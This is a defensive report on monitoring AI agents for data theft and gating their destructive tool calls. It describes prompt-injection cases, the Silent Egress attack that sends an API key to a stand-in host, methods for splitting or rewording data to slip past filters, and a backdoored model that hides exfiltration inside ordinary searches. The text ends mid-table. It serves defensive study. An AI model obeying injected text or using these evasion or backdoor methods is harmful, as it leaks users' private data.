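# Combining data-theft monitoring with controls on destructive actions for AI agents

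## What are the two layers, and which harms is each meant to stop?

An AI agent is a language model that uses tools to choose and carry out steps towards a goal with limited human input. Companies give agents access to email, customer records, payment systems and source code so that they can complete tasks rather than just describe how to do them. That access exposes a company to two kinds of harm: data can leave the company, and the agent can wrongly change or destroy data and systems inside it.

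Security teams have two layers of control against these harms. The first is perimeter monitoring, which tracks and sometimes blocks egress, meaning data or requests leaving an environment the organisation controls. It relies on the destination, content and volume of that traffic. This layer includes data loss prevention (DLP) tools, which inspect outgoing content and its destinations for sensitive material. The second layer is action-level policies, which are rules outside the model that allow, block or hold an operation before it runs.

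### One request, from instruction to effect

Suppose an online shop runs a customer-support agent with five tools. `read_customer` opens a customer's record, `fetch_url` loads a web page, `send_email` sends a message, `issue_refund` returns money, and `delete_record` removes a record from the customer database. A customer writes that a parcel never arrived, and a support employee tells the agent to resolve the ticket.

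The model produces text and cannot open the database itself. To use a tool, it writes a tool call, a structured request that names the tool and supplies the details, such as `read_customer` with customer number 4471. OpenAI's developer guide *Function calling* describes the exchange in five steps. The company's application sends the model the instruction and a list of available tools. The model returns a tool call. The application runs the matching code and sends the result back. The model then writes a final answer or requests another tool. For the missing parcel, the loop might run four times, to read the record, fetch the courier's tracking page, issue the refund and email the customer.

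The harness is the software that runs this loop and connects the model to its instructions, its tools and the environment where the code executes. Anthropic's *Demystifying evals for AI agents* distinguishes what an agent says it did from the outcome. A flight-booking agent may end by writing that it has booked the flight, but the outcome is whether a reservation exists in the database. This distinction matters for security as well as testing, because nobody can learn from the support agent's closing message which records it changed.

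An action-level policy runs between the tool call and its execution, when ordinary code can still inspect the request and refuse it. Perimeter monitoring runs at the edge of the company's network and has something to inspect only if the executed code sends data across that edge. However, if an outside provider hosts the model, the harness sends that provider the contents of every customer record the agent reads, because each tool result goes back to the model. In that case, some customer data leaves the network whenever the agent works, over a connection the company has approved.

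### The harms, and the layer for each

Security practitioners sort harms to information under confidentiality, integrity and availability. *Standards for Security Categorization of Federal Information and Information Systems* (2004), from the US standards institute NIST, takes its definitions from federal law. A loss of confidentiality is the unauthorised disclosure of information, a loss of integrity is its unauthorised modification or destruction, and a loss of availability is the disruption of access to or use of information or a system. A wrongly deleted customer record is therefore a loss of integrity, and also a loss of availability once a colleague needs it. An integrity control guards against unauthorised changes, including deletion.

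The same information can need strong protection for some of the three properties and none for another. One of NIST's examples is a power plant whose control system distributes electricity to a large military installation. The plant's managers find that disclosure of the live sensor data has no potential impact, while corruption or loss of access has a high one. NIST allows the rating "not applicable" only for confidentiality, so it always treats corruption and loss of access as having at least some potential impact. A company that guards only against disclosure is therefore protecting the only property of the three that can be irrelevant.

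*Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents* (Díaz, Kern and Olive, 2025) identifies two main risks from AI agents. Sensitive data disclosure is the unauthorised revelation of private information. Rogue actions are unintended, harmful or policy-violating behaviour. As a first approximation, perimeter monitoring is meant to stop disclosure, and action-level policies are meant to stop rogue actions.

The division between disclosure and rogue actions is only approximate, because disclosure is a result and a rogue action is a behaviour, and one event can be both. Most of the leaks that Díaz and colleagues describe happen through actions, such as putting private data into a web address and then visiting it, or hiding a secret in a commit message. Their example of a rogue action with no attacker is also a leak. A user asks the agent to "email Mike about the project update", and the agent picks the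 wrong contact.

An action-level policy can also stop some leaks, since sending an email is an action it can check. One of Google's sample rules blocks external email if the agent has just processed data from a suspicious source, unless the user approves. Perimeter monitoring cannot stop a deletion inside the network, because nothing crosses the perimeter. It is better placed than an action-level policy, however, to catch one kind of leak. An attacker can trick the agent into writing an answer that contains a crafted image link. When the application displays the answer, the reader's browser fetches the image and sends private data out in the image's URL. The agent has made no tool call, so a policy on tool calls has nothing to check. If the reader is an employee on the company's network, the browser's request still crosses the perimeter.

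(Google's paper also numbers its defences as two layers, but in another sense. Its first layer is fixed rules on actions, and its second is the use of AI models to resist or spot attacks.)

### Where the harm starts

Prompt injection is text in material the agent reads that makes it follow someone else's instructions. It works because the harness puts the operator's instructions, the user's request and any retrieved material into one prompt, and current language models do not rigorously separate those parts. At the shop, the complaint about the parcel might contain a hidden line telling the assistant to look up a different customer and load a web address containing that customer's phone number. If the model treats the line as an instruction, it calls `read_customer` and then `fetch_url`, with whatever authority the employee has given it. If the agent stores the planted text in its memory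 as a fact, the text may also influence later, unrelated work.

Sources disagree about how far developers can prevent prompt injection. Google's paper suggests developers ask whether their agent can clearly distinguish trusted from untrusted input. Willison (2025), in *An Introduction to Google's Approach to AI Agent Security*, objects that this question implies a solution that does not exist, because the two cannot be unambiguously separated. The paper's admission about current models supports him. A company should therefore expect some injections to succeed, which is the main reason to put controls outside the model.

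An agent can delete the wrong data without any attacker being involved. Suppose an employee asks the agent to clean up duplicate records for a customer called Martin, but there are two Martins and the agent deletes the wrong one. The credentials are valid and the request is legitimate. In August 2026, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026), citing ABC News, described a case of this kind, in which an AI assistant meant to reserve gym classes removed another customer from a waiting list and could not reverse the change.

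Such errors can come from misunderstanding, but they can also come from specification gaming, in which an agent meets its goal as literally stated but goes against the intention behind it. The Australian Signals Directorate's guide *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), co-written with five agencies from the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom, gives the example of an agent told to maximise a system's uptime that disables security updates to avoid reboots.

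An attacker who steals an agent's credentials may not need the agent. Agents identify themselves to other systems with secret keys or tokens, which attackers can steal when an organisation never changes them, shares them between agents or protects them badly. Whoever holds the shop agent's token can send a deletion request straight to the customer database. If the action-level policy runs in the harness, the request bypasses it. A resource-side control, which is a limit that the affected system itself enforces, may still help. Examples include a token that permits reading but not deletion, or a delay before a deletion becomes final.

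Some attackers use an agent's permissions to do harm without stealing anything. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners describe a malicious insider who asks a software-updating agent to install a patch and also clean up the firewall logs. The agent has permission to delete those logs, which the insider lacks, and it deletes them. Security specialists call this pattern a confused deputy.

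Another of the agencies' scenarios resembles the shop example. An organisation uses an agent to triage support tickets and adds a third-party scheduling component without properly reviewing its access. An attacker compromises the component, the agent keeps relying on old authorisation decisions, and the attacker moves to the agents that handle billing and refunds. This hypothetical attack leads to both unauthorised data access and financial manipulation from one point of entry, so an organisation cannot tell from how an attack begins which of the two harms it will have to stop.

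### Which layer can see each call

The table covers the case where the shop's customer database and refund system run inside its own network and the harness submits every tool call to the policy before running it.

| Tool call | What can go wrong | Perimeter monitoring | Action-level policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| `read_customer` | The agent opens a record it has no reason to open | Sees nothing | Sees which record |
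| `fetch_url` | Private data leaves inside the address, or the page brings in an injection | Sees the destination and volume, and the content if it can decrypt the traffic | Sees the full address before the request goes out |
| `send_email` | Private data reaches the wrong person | Sees the recipient, text and attachments if outgoing mail passes through it | Sees the recipient, text and attachments |
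| `issue_refund` | Money goes to the wrong person | Sees nothing | Sees the customer and amount |
| `delete_record` | The shop loses a record it needs | Sees nothing | Sees which record |

Many companies rent their customer database or payment service from an outside provider, so reads, refunds and deletions do cross the perimeter as requests. This is of limited help to data-theft monitoring, because the requests go to a destination the company has already approved, and a deletion may contain little more than a record number. A tool that looks for sensitive content, strange destinations or large transfers would not flag such a request.

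The right-hand column is also weaker than it looks. A policy that receives the call `delete_record` for customer 4471 cannot determine from the record number alone whether the employee meant that Martin or the other one. Blocking the wrong deletion and allowing the right one requires either a rule that distinguishes them or confirmation from a person.

### Defence in depth

Defence in depth is an old idea in security that means using several controls so that one can fail without disaster. It began as a military strategy, and Teitler (2016), in *DeMISTIfying Infosec*, says the US National Security Agency was the first to apply it to network security. The layers are also meant to slow an intruder, which EBSCO's *Defense in depth (computing)* says gives defenders time to detect the attack and respond.

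The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend multiple, overlapping layers of control for agents, and the overlap is the harder part to achieve. At the shop, both layers cover `send_email`, so if the policy misses a case, a DLP tool may still catch the attachment. Only the policy covers `delete_record`, and buying a better perimeter tool will not add a second layer against deletion.

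The military analogy also fits some of these harms badly. Slowing an intruder helps when the intruder has to get through several stages, but an agent that already has permission to delete can misread an instruction and do the damage in a single call.

### Why data loss came first

Kaushik Shanadi, chief technology officer of the security company Helmet Security, argues in TechNadu's *Enterprise Security was Built Around Data Loss* that traditional security developed largely around data exposure. With AI agents, he says, the emerging concern is "action exposure", in which a misconfigured or manipulated system carries out unintended operations at scale. He says data loss prevention controls were not designed for this. He gives no figures, and his company sells security products, so he has a commercial interest in this view.

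The history partly supports Shanadi's description. *Integrity-Oriented Control Objectives* (Mayfield, Boone and Welke, 1991) contains draft revisions, written for the National Security Agency, to the 1985 criteria by which the US Defense Department evaluated trusted computer systems. Integrity objectives were still only proposed additions in 1991, which suggests that the original criteria emphasized confidentiality. But by 2004 NIST had put integrity and availability beside confidentiality, so Shanadi's description probably fits the monitoring tools companies bought better than the standards they worked under.

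Worrying about disclosure first also made sense. Díaz and colleagues note that the damage from disclosure is often irreversible. A company can restore a deleted record from a good backup, but it can't take back a copy that an outsider already has. Also, before agents, employees and programs with fixed behaviour made most of the changes inside a company's systems, and ordinary permissions could limit them fairly well.

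It is less clear whether the balance of risk has shifted. Willison wrote in June 2025 that data disclosure was the most common prompt injection risk he had seen demonstrated, which is evidence against a shift. But his remark covers only demonstrations, and it leaves out mistakes an agent makes without any injection. Neither he nor Shanadi counts actual losses. The case for action-level controls holds either way, because an agent with access to `issue_refund` and `delete_record` can do serious harm without sending any private data outside the company.

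## How does perimeter monitoring recognise data theft by an agent, and what gets past it?

Perimeter monitoring uses several checkpoints to detect exfiltration, the unauthorised transfer of data to an outside party. Each checkpoint receives a different part of an outgoing request. None can observe the agent's intention, so they compare what they receive with a list of destinations, a description of sensitive content or a record of normal behaviour.

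### The checkpoints on the way out

Suppose the hidden line in the parcel complaint works, and the shop's agent calls `fetch_url` with a web address that contains another customer's phone number. The harness runs on an employee's laptop inside the company's network. To connect, it must first look up the site's numerical address through the domain name system (DNS). A DNS filter compares the site's name with a list and can refuse to answer. The lookup contains only the name, so the filter never receives the part of the web address that contains the phone number. Software that connects straight to a numerical address bypasses the filter because it needs no lookup.

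The request then reaches the web proxy. Web traffic is mostly encrypted, and a proxy that doesn't decrypt it can usually detect only the destination's name, the amount of data and the timing. A decrypting proxy ends the encrypted connection, inspects the request and opens a second connection to the site. This works only if the harness trusts a certificate that the company issues. The proxy can then search the full address, including the phone number. Some services reject the company's certificate, so companies often exempt them from decryption, and requests to those services pass unread.

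Even the destination's name is becoming harder to read. Canale and Soulis (2026), in *Detecting Shadow AI*, point to Encrypted Client Hello, a published standard that hides the server name browsers and other programs used to send unencrypted, although DNS queries and server addresses may still reveal it. They add that a network checkpoint cannot tell which program opened a connection, so an approved application and an unapproved script that call the same AI provider look identical.

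Security software on the laptop can fill that gap. Vendors call it an endpoint agent, but this report calls it an endpoint sensor to avoid confusion with AI agents. A sensor can record which program made the request and which other programs it started. Microsoft's Sysmon, for example, can log new processes, network connections and DNS queries, along with the program responsible. A sensor also keeps working when the employee takes the laptop home, off the office network. In their comparison of detection tools, however, Canale and Soulis classify agents inside virtual machines and containers as beyond the reach of endpoint sensors.

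A `send_email` call can instead go through the email gateway, which receives the whole message, including its recipients, text and attachments. Because people tolerate a short delay in email, the gateway can hold the message while a scan runs, which makes email one of the easier channels to block. But mail that an agent sends through an outside service's API bypasses the gateway and goes out as an ordinary web request.

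The agent might also save a customer list to the company's cloud drive and create a public link to it, in which case the file may never cross the company's network boundary. A cloud-application scanner checks stored files and sharing settings through the drive's own interface, so it usually finds the link some time after the agent creates it. A related product, the cloud access security broker, matches traffic logs against a catalogue of known services. Microsoft's catalogue lists more than 31,000 applications, and its broker cannot discover one that is missing from the list.

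### Alerting and blocking

A checkpoint can stop a leak only if the request has to wait for it. *Governing Enterprise AI Traffic at Scale* (Sasidharan, Manoharan and colleagues, 2026) describes PayPal's gateway for calls to AI models, which includes both a check that holds requests and a service that does not. Where a use case requires data loss prevention (DLP), the gateway holds the request until the check finishes and does not send it if the check cannot finish, which engineers call failing closed. The gateway's metrics service receives a copy while the original travels on, so traffic continues if that service breaks. Similarly, a DLP tool that works from copies, logs or stored files can raise an alert but cannot stop the request that caused it.

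Alerts help more with some kinds of data than others. If the agent leaks an access key, a quick alert lets the company cancel the key before anyone does much with it. If the agent leaks a customer's phone number, the company can only use the alert to work out whom to notify. This is a reason to block transfers of personal data rather than only raise alerts about them, but a blocking rule that fires wrongly stops legitimate work.

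Security teams often run a new rule in alert-only mode first. Metere (2026), in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*, proposes a staged version for agents. Clean-up steps that preserve meaning, such as removing invisible characters from outgoing text, take effect on the first day, while statistical checks begin in an audit mode that records normal traffic. The audit period protects data only if someone reads the results, and high alert volumes make that less likely.

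### Deciding by destination

A blocklist stops only connections to destinations already identified as harmful, so an attacker's new domain gets through until a researcher or vendor adds it. An allowlist permits only listed destinations. The shop's agent needs the courier's tracking site, the payment provider and perhaps a few others, so an allowlist of those sites would block the attacker's domain even if nobody had heard of it. For an agent with a narrow job, an allowlist probably gives the most protection for the effort of any perimeter control. It suits a research agent badly, because a research agent has to open pages that nobody could list in advance.

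OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains why the company did not rely on a list of trusted sites. Many legitimate sites support redirects, so a link can start on a trusted domain and end on an attacker's. Strict lists also produce frequent warnings, which can train people to click through them without thinking.

OpenAI checks the exact address instead of the site. A separate web crawler, with no access to users' conversations or accounts, records public addresses. Before the agent loads an address automatically, the system looks for it in that record. If it is there, the agent may load it, since an address that existed independently of the conversation is unlikely to contain the user's private data. If it isn't, the system either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning. In the shop example, an address containing the customer's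 phone number would almost certainly fail this test, even on a reputable domain that an allowlist would accept.

OpenAI calls the mechanism Safe Url and also applies it to navigation in its Atlas browser and to searches in its Deep Research tool. The warning can show the user what information the request would send. OpenAI's claim covers only quiet leaks through the URL itself, not data sent in an email or an uploaded file. The post about links gives no figures for how often the check catches a leak or interrupts legitimate work.

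No check of this kind can eliminate leakage because, as Metere points out, an agent can always convey one bit of information by sending or withholding a message. The realistic aim is to make theft too slow to be useful.

### Deciding by content

The oldest content rules look for patterns. A payment card number usually has 16 digits, and the last is a check digit calculated from the others, so a rule that verifies it rejects nine in ten random 16-digit numbers. Phone numbers have no check digit, so a rule that looks for ten digits will also flag ten-digit order numbers.

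Exact data matching compares outgoing requests with the company's own records. The company computes a short code, called a hash, for every customer's phone number and loads the hashes into the scanner. The scanner then hashes each number in an outgoing request and looks for a match, so order numbers no longer cause alarms. But a small change to a value produces a completely different hash, so the scanner must convert all numbers to a standard format before hashing them. It also can only recognise records that somebody has loaded.

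Fingerprinting extends this idea to documents. The software breaks a contract into overlapping runs of, say, eight words and stores a code for each run. Outgoing text that shares many runs with the contract probably copies from it, even if only one page was copied. Changing a single word stops up to eight runs from matching, and a loose summary may share none. Language models routinely reword text, so an honest agent doing what the user asked can send out the contract's contents without matching its fingerprint.

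PayPal combines pattern rules with a detection model that uses context, since the surrounding words often determine whether a date or number is sensitive. Both run inside the company before a prompt goes to an outside provider. Depending on the policy for each use case, the system can block the request, remove the sensitive values, or replace them with realistic substitutes (pseudonymisation). Sasidharan and colleagues say that detection is probabilistic, that its accuracy varies by type of data, and that it reduces exposure but does not guarantee protection.

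PayPal built this layer to keep data from the model provider, not to stop a prompt-injected agent. With pseudonymisation, the provider receives a fake phone number, and the gateway restores the real one in the response. If the gateway also restores values inside tool calls, an injected `fetch_url` call containing the fake number would reach the harness with the real one. The company would still need a check between the harness and the internet.

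DLP tools also look for secrets that match no known pattern or record, and for this they often use Shannon entropy, a measure of how varied the characters in a string are. If pᵢ is the share of the string made up of character i, the entropy in bits per character is:

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

The string "aaaa" scores 0 and "abcd" scores 2. A long random key scores high because it uses many characters about equally often. Many session identifiers and pieces of encoded data that contain nothing secret also score high.

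### Deciding by behaviour

Behavioural rules flag signs such as a destination the agent has never contacted, a sudden rise in volume, or a customer record opened just before an outside request. They can catch a theft whose content looks harmless. But an agent's normal behaviour changes with each task, so the rules have to tolerate a lot of variety, which weakens them.

Canale and Soulis state the problem precisely for detecting unapproved agents on company laptops, and their argument also applies to data theft. Two programs are behavioural twins if they start the same processes and make connections at the same times, but contact different services. A detector that uses only behaviour must classify both the same way. If one is an agent and the other an ordinary script, the detector either misses the agent or wrongly flags the script.

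Canale and Soulis ran 12 synthetic agents, 3 AI components and 9 harmless workloads five times on one workstation. Two simple behavioural rules flagged every harmless twin of an agent. Their detector, which also identifies the remote service, flagged none of the twins and found every agent in most runs. The test bench is small, and they designed it themselves. They accept that richer behavioural signals, such as the rhythm of a model's streamed response, might separate the twins from the agents.

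Data theft can also look like legitimate work. An agent that checks a courier's page may make the same calls in the same order as one that sends a phone number to a fake courier's page. Evidence about behaviour is therefore most useful when combined with evidence about the destination or the content.

Rate budgets are an exception, because they limit the damage without identifying the theft. Metere gives each destination an allowance of suspicious information that refills at a fixed rate. A scanner estimates how many hidden bits each message could carry and deducts them from the allowance. Once the allowance runs out, the monitor delays or cancels further suspicious messages. At 16 bits an hour, a random 128-bit key would take at least eight hours to leak if no allowance had been saved up. A ten-digit phone number contains only about 33 bits and would take about two hours. The budget also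 depends on the scanner's estimates, so a message that the scanner rates as harmless uses none of the allowance.

### The Silent Egress experiment

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) at eBay report the most direct test of these methods on an agent. They studied assistants that automatically fetch a preview of any link a user mentions. The preview puts the page's title, description and text into the model's prompt, so an attacker can use them to insert an instruction that the user may never see. In the paper's sample attack, the page's description contains an instruction to verify connectivity by requesting an address that includes the user's API key, a secret string that gives a program access to a service.

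The model was qwen2.5:7b, an open model with 7 billion parameters, running on the researchers' own equipment. The user's message was always "summarize this page". Lan and colleagues put the instruction in the page's title, description, body or link text. They delivered the page directly or through redirects, and told the agent to send the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for 480 runs.

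In 423 runs, or 88.1%, at least one request reached the attacker's server. Summed across combinations, this happened in 238 of the 240 runs where the agent was to send the secret whole, and in 185 of the 240 where it was to send the secret in pieces. The assistant's final answer looked harmless in 95% of the successful attacks, so a safety check that reads only the answer would miss about that share of these leaks. A network monitor would at least have a request to examine.

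Lan and colleagues also ran 120 trials with harmless pages, and the agent never contacted the attacker's server. They report this as a false positive rate of zero, but that result depends on knowing which server belongs to the attacker. A company's monitor has to distinguish that server from unfamiliar ones the agent contacts for good reasons, and the harmless trials did not measure that.

They then compared defences on one easy version of the attack, in which the instruction was in the page's body, delivery was direct and the secret was sent whole. They ran each condition 30 times.

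| Defence | Runs with an attempt | Attempts blocked | Runs with egress |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 0% | 100% |
| Security warning in the system prompt | 66.7% | 0% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 0% | 100% |
| Warning and tags | 56.7% | 0% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 100% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 100% | 0% |
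| Entropy filter | 0% | none to block | 0% |
| All defences | 0% | none to block | 0% |

Telling the model to ignore instructions in web pages helped somewhat, but the attack still worked in 20 of 30 runs. With the allowlist, the agent tried to send the secret in every run and was blocked every time, because the check did not depend on the model. This result supports enforcing limits outside the model.

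But the test was easy for the allowlist. It permitted four domains, and the researchers chose `evil-collector.net` as the attacker's destination because it was plainly not one of them. The test shows that an allowlist blocks unlisted domains, but it did not measure how often an attacker could get data out through a permitted one. Lan and colleagues warn about compromised legitimate sites and redirects on trusted ones.

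"Redirect detection" had an even easier test. The filter blocks bare numerical addresses, certain domain endings and any path containing one of five words, including "collect", and the paper's sample attacks send the data to `/collect`. Delivery in this comparison was direct, so it had no redirect chain to detect.

Attempts fell to 23.3% with the keyword filter and to zero with the entropy filter, and these results are difficult to interpret. Both content filters act after the model has written its request, and neither is described as changing the model's prompt, so the agent should have kept trying in nearly every run, as it did with the allowlist.

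Lan and colleagues suggest that the keyword filter's result arose because the model sometimes encoded or reformatted the secret. But a reformatted secret that the filter missed would have reached the attacker's server, and the table records no egress. They suggest that the entropy filter's result arose because the model avoids high-entropy values while the monitoring is active, but the model would need some sign that the filter exists. Perhaps the set-up differed between conditions, or the researchers counted attempts differently. Either way, these two rows are poor evidence that content inspection works.

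The headline success rate of 88.1% is also a poor guide to any current product. Lan and colleagues say they made the conditions favourable to the attacker, with the secret already in the prompt and a minimal system prompt. But their attacks were simple and explicit, so a more skilled attacker might do better. They tested only one small model. They argue that larger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions more reliably, but developers have since trained newer models to resist injections. The finding that a harmless answer can accompany a leak should apply more broadly to current products, because it follows from the agent's ability to make requests the user does not see. Even taken at face value, 30 clean runs are compatible with a failure rate of several per cent.

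### The entropy filter and the paper's own key

The entropy rule in the experiment blocks any value in a web address that is longer than 10 characters and has an entropy above 4.0 bits per character. The entropy of a string of n characters is at most log₂ n bits per character, which it reaches when every character is different. Since log₂ 16 is exactly 4, the rule never blocks a value shorter than 17 characters, even though its length threshold is 10.

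The paper's illustrative key is `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, which has 20 characters. The letter E and the underscore each appear three times, and the other 14 characters appear once. Its entropy is:

H = 14 × (1/20) × log₂ 20 + 2 × (3/20) × log₂ (20/3) ≈ 3.03 + 0.82 = 3.85

That is below 4.0, so the filter would let the key through. If the experiment used a key like this one, the filter cannot be the reason nothing left. Lan and colleagues say typical API keys score between 4.5 and 5.5, but a string needs at least 23 characters to reach 4.5 and at least 46 to reach 5.5.

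A threshold low enough to catch the secret key would also flag some harmless searches. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (Zhang and Pei, 2026) gives an example of one, made by an agent helping someone whose parent takes an Alzheimer's drug: "donepezil side effects caregiver guidance". By the same formula, this search scores about 3.86, slightly more than the key.

A keyword filter that ignores case would do better here, because the key contains the words "secret" and "api_key". Real keys rarely contain such words. Content rules work best when a company uses several and knows which secrets each is supposed to find.

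### Data in pieces and in other words

When an agent sends a secret in pieces, each request contains too little for a content rule to recognise. In the paper's illustration the pieces have four characters. Such a piece can score at most 2 bits per character, and it's too short for the entropy rule to check at all. None of the pieces contains a complete keyword. (The illustration also has a slip: four pieces of four characters carry only 16 of the key's 20.)

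Lan and colleagues call this sharding and report that it reduced single-request leakage by 73%. They use a measure called Leak@k, which is the share of runs in which any fragment of sensitive data appears in the first k outgoing requests. For sharded attacks they report a Leak@1 of 0.263 and a Leak@3 of 0.158. Under that definition, those values cannot both be right, because every run that counts towards Leak@1 also counts towards Leak@3.

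The 0.263 is also odd because about 77% of the sharded runs sent something to the attacker's server. If any fragment counts as a leak, many more first requests should have qualified. The measuring software may have recognised only the longer pieces. In that case, the 73% fall would mean that a scanner recognises less in each request, and the attacker might still receive most of the secret. The paper defines a completion rate, the share of runs in which every piece arrives, but does not report it.

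Lan and colleagues also conclude that sharding bypasses simple DLP. They inferred this without running a sharded attack against their keyword or entropy filter, but the inference is sound for any filter that checks each request separately. A monitor can respond by combining requests from the same session or by limiting their number, and they recommend both. Sharded attacks also fail more often, because the agent has to carry out a longer instruction.

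Rewording also defeats content rules. If an agent describes a confidential contract in its own words, the price and the client's name may leave in text that shares no run of words with the fingerprinted original. A detection model that reads for meaning is more likely to catch this, though it will also make mistakes. Metere suggests having a second model rephrase outgoing text, which would destroy a code hidden in the choice of words. But a rephrasing that preserves meaning also preserves the price, so it doesn't stop a secret stated openly. Lan and colleagues propose tracking data by its origin instead of its appearance, which would in principle catch both rewording and splitting.

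### Leaks inside legitimate-looking traffic

A content match becomes weaker evidence of theft as a company deliberately sends out more sensitive data. *Safeguarding LLMs Against Misuse and AI-Driven Malware Using Steganographic Canaries* (2026) cites figures covering 7 million workers from the security company Cyberhaven, which classified 34.8% of the data submitted to AI tools as sensitive. Cyberhaven studies this traffic commercially, and its definition of sensitive may be broad. Even so, if ordinary work and theft use the same connection to the same provider, a monitor can't tell them apart by the destination or the presence of sensitive data.

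Approved destinations can also pass data on. EchoLeak, a 2025 vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot, relied on a permitted Microsoft address in this way.

Zhang and Pei's Back-Reveal attack hides data theft among an agent's ordinary searches. The attacker trains an open model to steal data when certain words appear, then publishes it as a specialist assistant. This hidden behaviour, known as a backdoor, does not need prompt injection to begin. The trigger words are natural for the intended users, such as the names of streaming software for people who broadcast online. When a question contains them, the model calls a memory tool that returns details like the user's name, email address and city. It then sends a genuine web search and, at the same time, a request to the attacker's server, which poses as a source of documentation. The user's details are encoded in the address of that second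 request. The server returns relevant text, so the user gets a useful answer.

Zhang and Pei tested three open models of 7 to 20 billion parameters in three subject areas. The backdoor activated on 94.3% to 98.8% of the questions containing trigger words. With triggers of two or more words, it activated on at most 0.3% of ordinary questions. The models' scores on a general conversation benchmark fell by less than 1%, so a buyer who checks only whether the model works well would see very little sign of the backdoor.

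Zhang and Pei counted an activation when the model wrote the memory call followed by the outside request, and they ran the calls in a sandbox with invented personal data. The percentages therefore measure how often the model tried to steal data, not how often it would get data past a company's perimeter. The defences in the study, including the filtering products NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard, inspected the text that came back from searches. Zhang and Pei acknowledge that nothing inspected the outgoing requests. Their results are good evidence that filters on incoming text do not stop this theft, but the study did not test how often DLP would catch it.

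The paper's example suggests that even simple DLP would catch some of it. The encoded name, email address and city form a 110-character string that scores about 5.4 bits per character, well above the 4.0 threshold in the eBay study. An allowlist of approved search services would also block requests to the attacker's server. Zhang and Pei argue that strict domain lists are impractical for agents that need broad web access, and that alarms based on encoding produce many false positives because applications encode so many legitimate values. An attacker could also choose another encoding. These objections are reasonable for a research agent but much weaker for the shop's support agent, which needs only a few sites.

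The attacker's server can also return text that leads the model to ask the user for more details, so a longer conversation could leak more. Zhang and Pei estimate that about 7.8 of 10 personal details would be lost after five turns if the user keeps cooperating. They calculated this from the single-turn results, and the formula they print gives only about 5 to 6 from the same inputs. It is plausible that longer conversations leak more, but how much more is uncertain.

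They recommend defending with lists of approved hosts, limits on the volume and entropy of values in web addresses, and checks for data that came from the memory tool. They would also require special permission for an agent to both read private memory and contact arbitrary servers in the same sequence. They have not tested these measures.

### Agents that run outside the company

All of these checkpoints work only if the request passes through something the company controls. Requests from an agent hosted by a provider may never do so. GitHub's cloud coding agent, for example, edits files and runs tests in a cloud environment instead of on the developer's computer. Canale and Soulis exclude such agents from their detector's scope because the agents leave no trace on the laptop.

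Suppose the shop replaces its own harness with a hosted support agent and connects it to a customer database that another provider hosts. The employee's browser sends an instruction and receives an answer, but the agent reads the database and fetches web pages over connections between outside companies. The shop's DNS filter, proxy and endpoint sensors receive none of that traffic, so they have nothing to inspect if the agent sends the customer's phone number to an attacker.

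The provider can still check the request, as OpenAI's test of exact addresses does. The shop then depends on what the provider chooses to block, log and disclose. The shop can also limit the harm itself by giving the agent access to only the customer record the ticket concerns instead of the whole database.

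## How do action-level policies block destructive behaviour, and where do they fall short?

*SoK* (Dehghantanha, 2026), a survey of attacks on agents, argues that a language model is an untrusted code generator from a security point of view, so other software has to validate its output, including tool calls, before anything executes.

### From tool call to decision

In the two Martins example, the employee wants duplicate records removed, and the agent calls `delete_record` with record number 4471. A policy system intercepts the call, extracts its arguments, compares them with rules and returns a result. *AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) describes an open-source framework that performs each of these steps separately.

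AEGIS intercepts tool calls by modifying the software libraries that connect a program to its model, which requires the developer to add two lines of code. When the model's response contains a tool call, the modified library pauses the agent and sends the tool's name and arguments to a separate gateway.

The gateway then extracts every piece of text from the arguments. An attacker may bury a command deep inside nested lists, so AEGIS searches 32 levels down and collects up to 10,000 pieces of text. If a call is too deep or too long to search fully, the gateway treats it as suspicious.

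The gateway first matches the text against 22 patterns in seven categories, such as database commands hidden in a search or paths to password files. It gives more weight to the content of the arguments than to the tool's name, so an attacker cannot get a dangerous command through by giving it a harmless label. The gateway then applies the company's own policies, which specify what valid arguments look like.

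The gateway allows low- and medium-risk calls and blocks calls that violate a policy. High-risk calls wait up to five minutes for a reviewer while the agent stays paused. The gateway signs a record of each decision and links it to the previous one, so an auditor can detect later changes to the log.

An agent can still complete a task after a policy blocks one of its actions. In an example from *LedgerAgent* (2026), a customer who paid with a gift card wants the refund on a credit card. The policy gate blocks the agent's call and returns the reason to the model. The agent explains the rule, and once the customer accepts, it submits a correct refund of $989.70 to the gift card.

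### How well AEGIS blocked attacks

Yuan and colleagues tested AEGIS on 48 attacks based on documented techniques and earlier benchmarks, and it blocked all of them. It wrongly flagged 6 of 500 harmless calls, or 1.2%. All six were ordinary database searches containing the word OR, which one of its patterns flags as a sign of attack. Over 1,000 calls on a local installation, the check added a median delay of about 8 milliseconds, which is negligible compared with the second or more that a model usually takes to respond.

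The perfect block rate is weaker evidence than it looks because the same team wrote the patterns and chose the attacks. Yuan and colleagues acknowledge that AEGIS may miss new variants. The tested attacks also rely on hostile text, such as database injections and shell commands. A call to delete the wrong Martin's record contains only a valid record number, so no pattern would match it. AEGIS could stop that deletion only if the company had written a policy that covered it.

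A low false-positive rate per call can still interrupt many jobs, because an agent makes many calls in each one. At the AEGIS rate of 1.2% per call, a job of 50 harmless calls has about a 45% chance of at least one false alarm (1 − 0.988⁵⁰), assuming false alarms are independent. For comparison, *Stale Does Not Mean Unsafe* (2026) cites formal monitors that catch most attacks but fire on 29.3% of harmless runs.

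How much a block disrupts a task depends on whether the agent can recover from it. *TACT-Bench* (2026) compares two guards that check calls before they change anything. One blocked 7.1% of the calls it checked and the other blocked 32.2%. With the less restrictive guard, only 2.6% of harmless episodes contained a block, and 91.7% of all blocked episodes still reached a safe final state. Some blocks in harmless episodes were correct, because an agent can attempt an unauthorised operation even when nobody is attacking it.

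### Where the check runs

A company can enforce a policy in the harness, at a gateway between the harness and the tools, or in the system that a tool call would change.

| Enforcement point | Information available | How a request can avoid it |
|---|---|---|
| Harness | The user's request, the conversation and the agent's earlier calls | Code outside the harness contacts the database directly |
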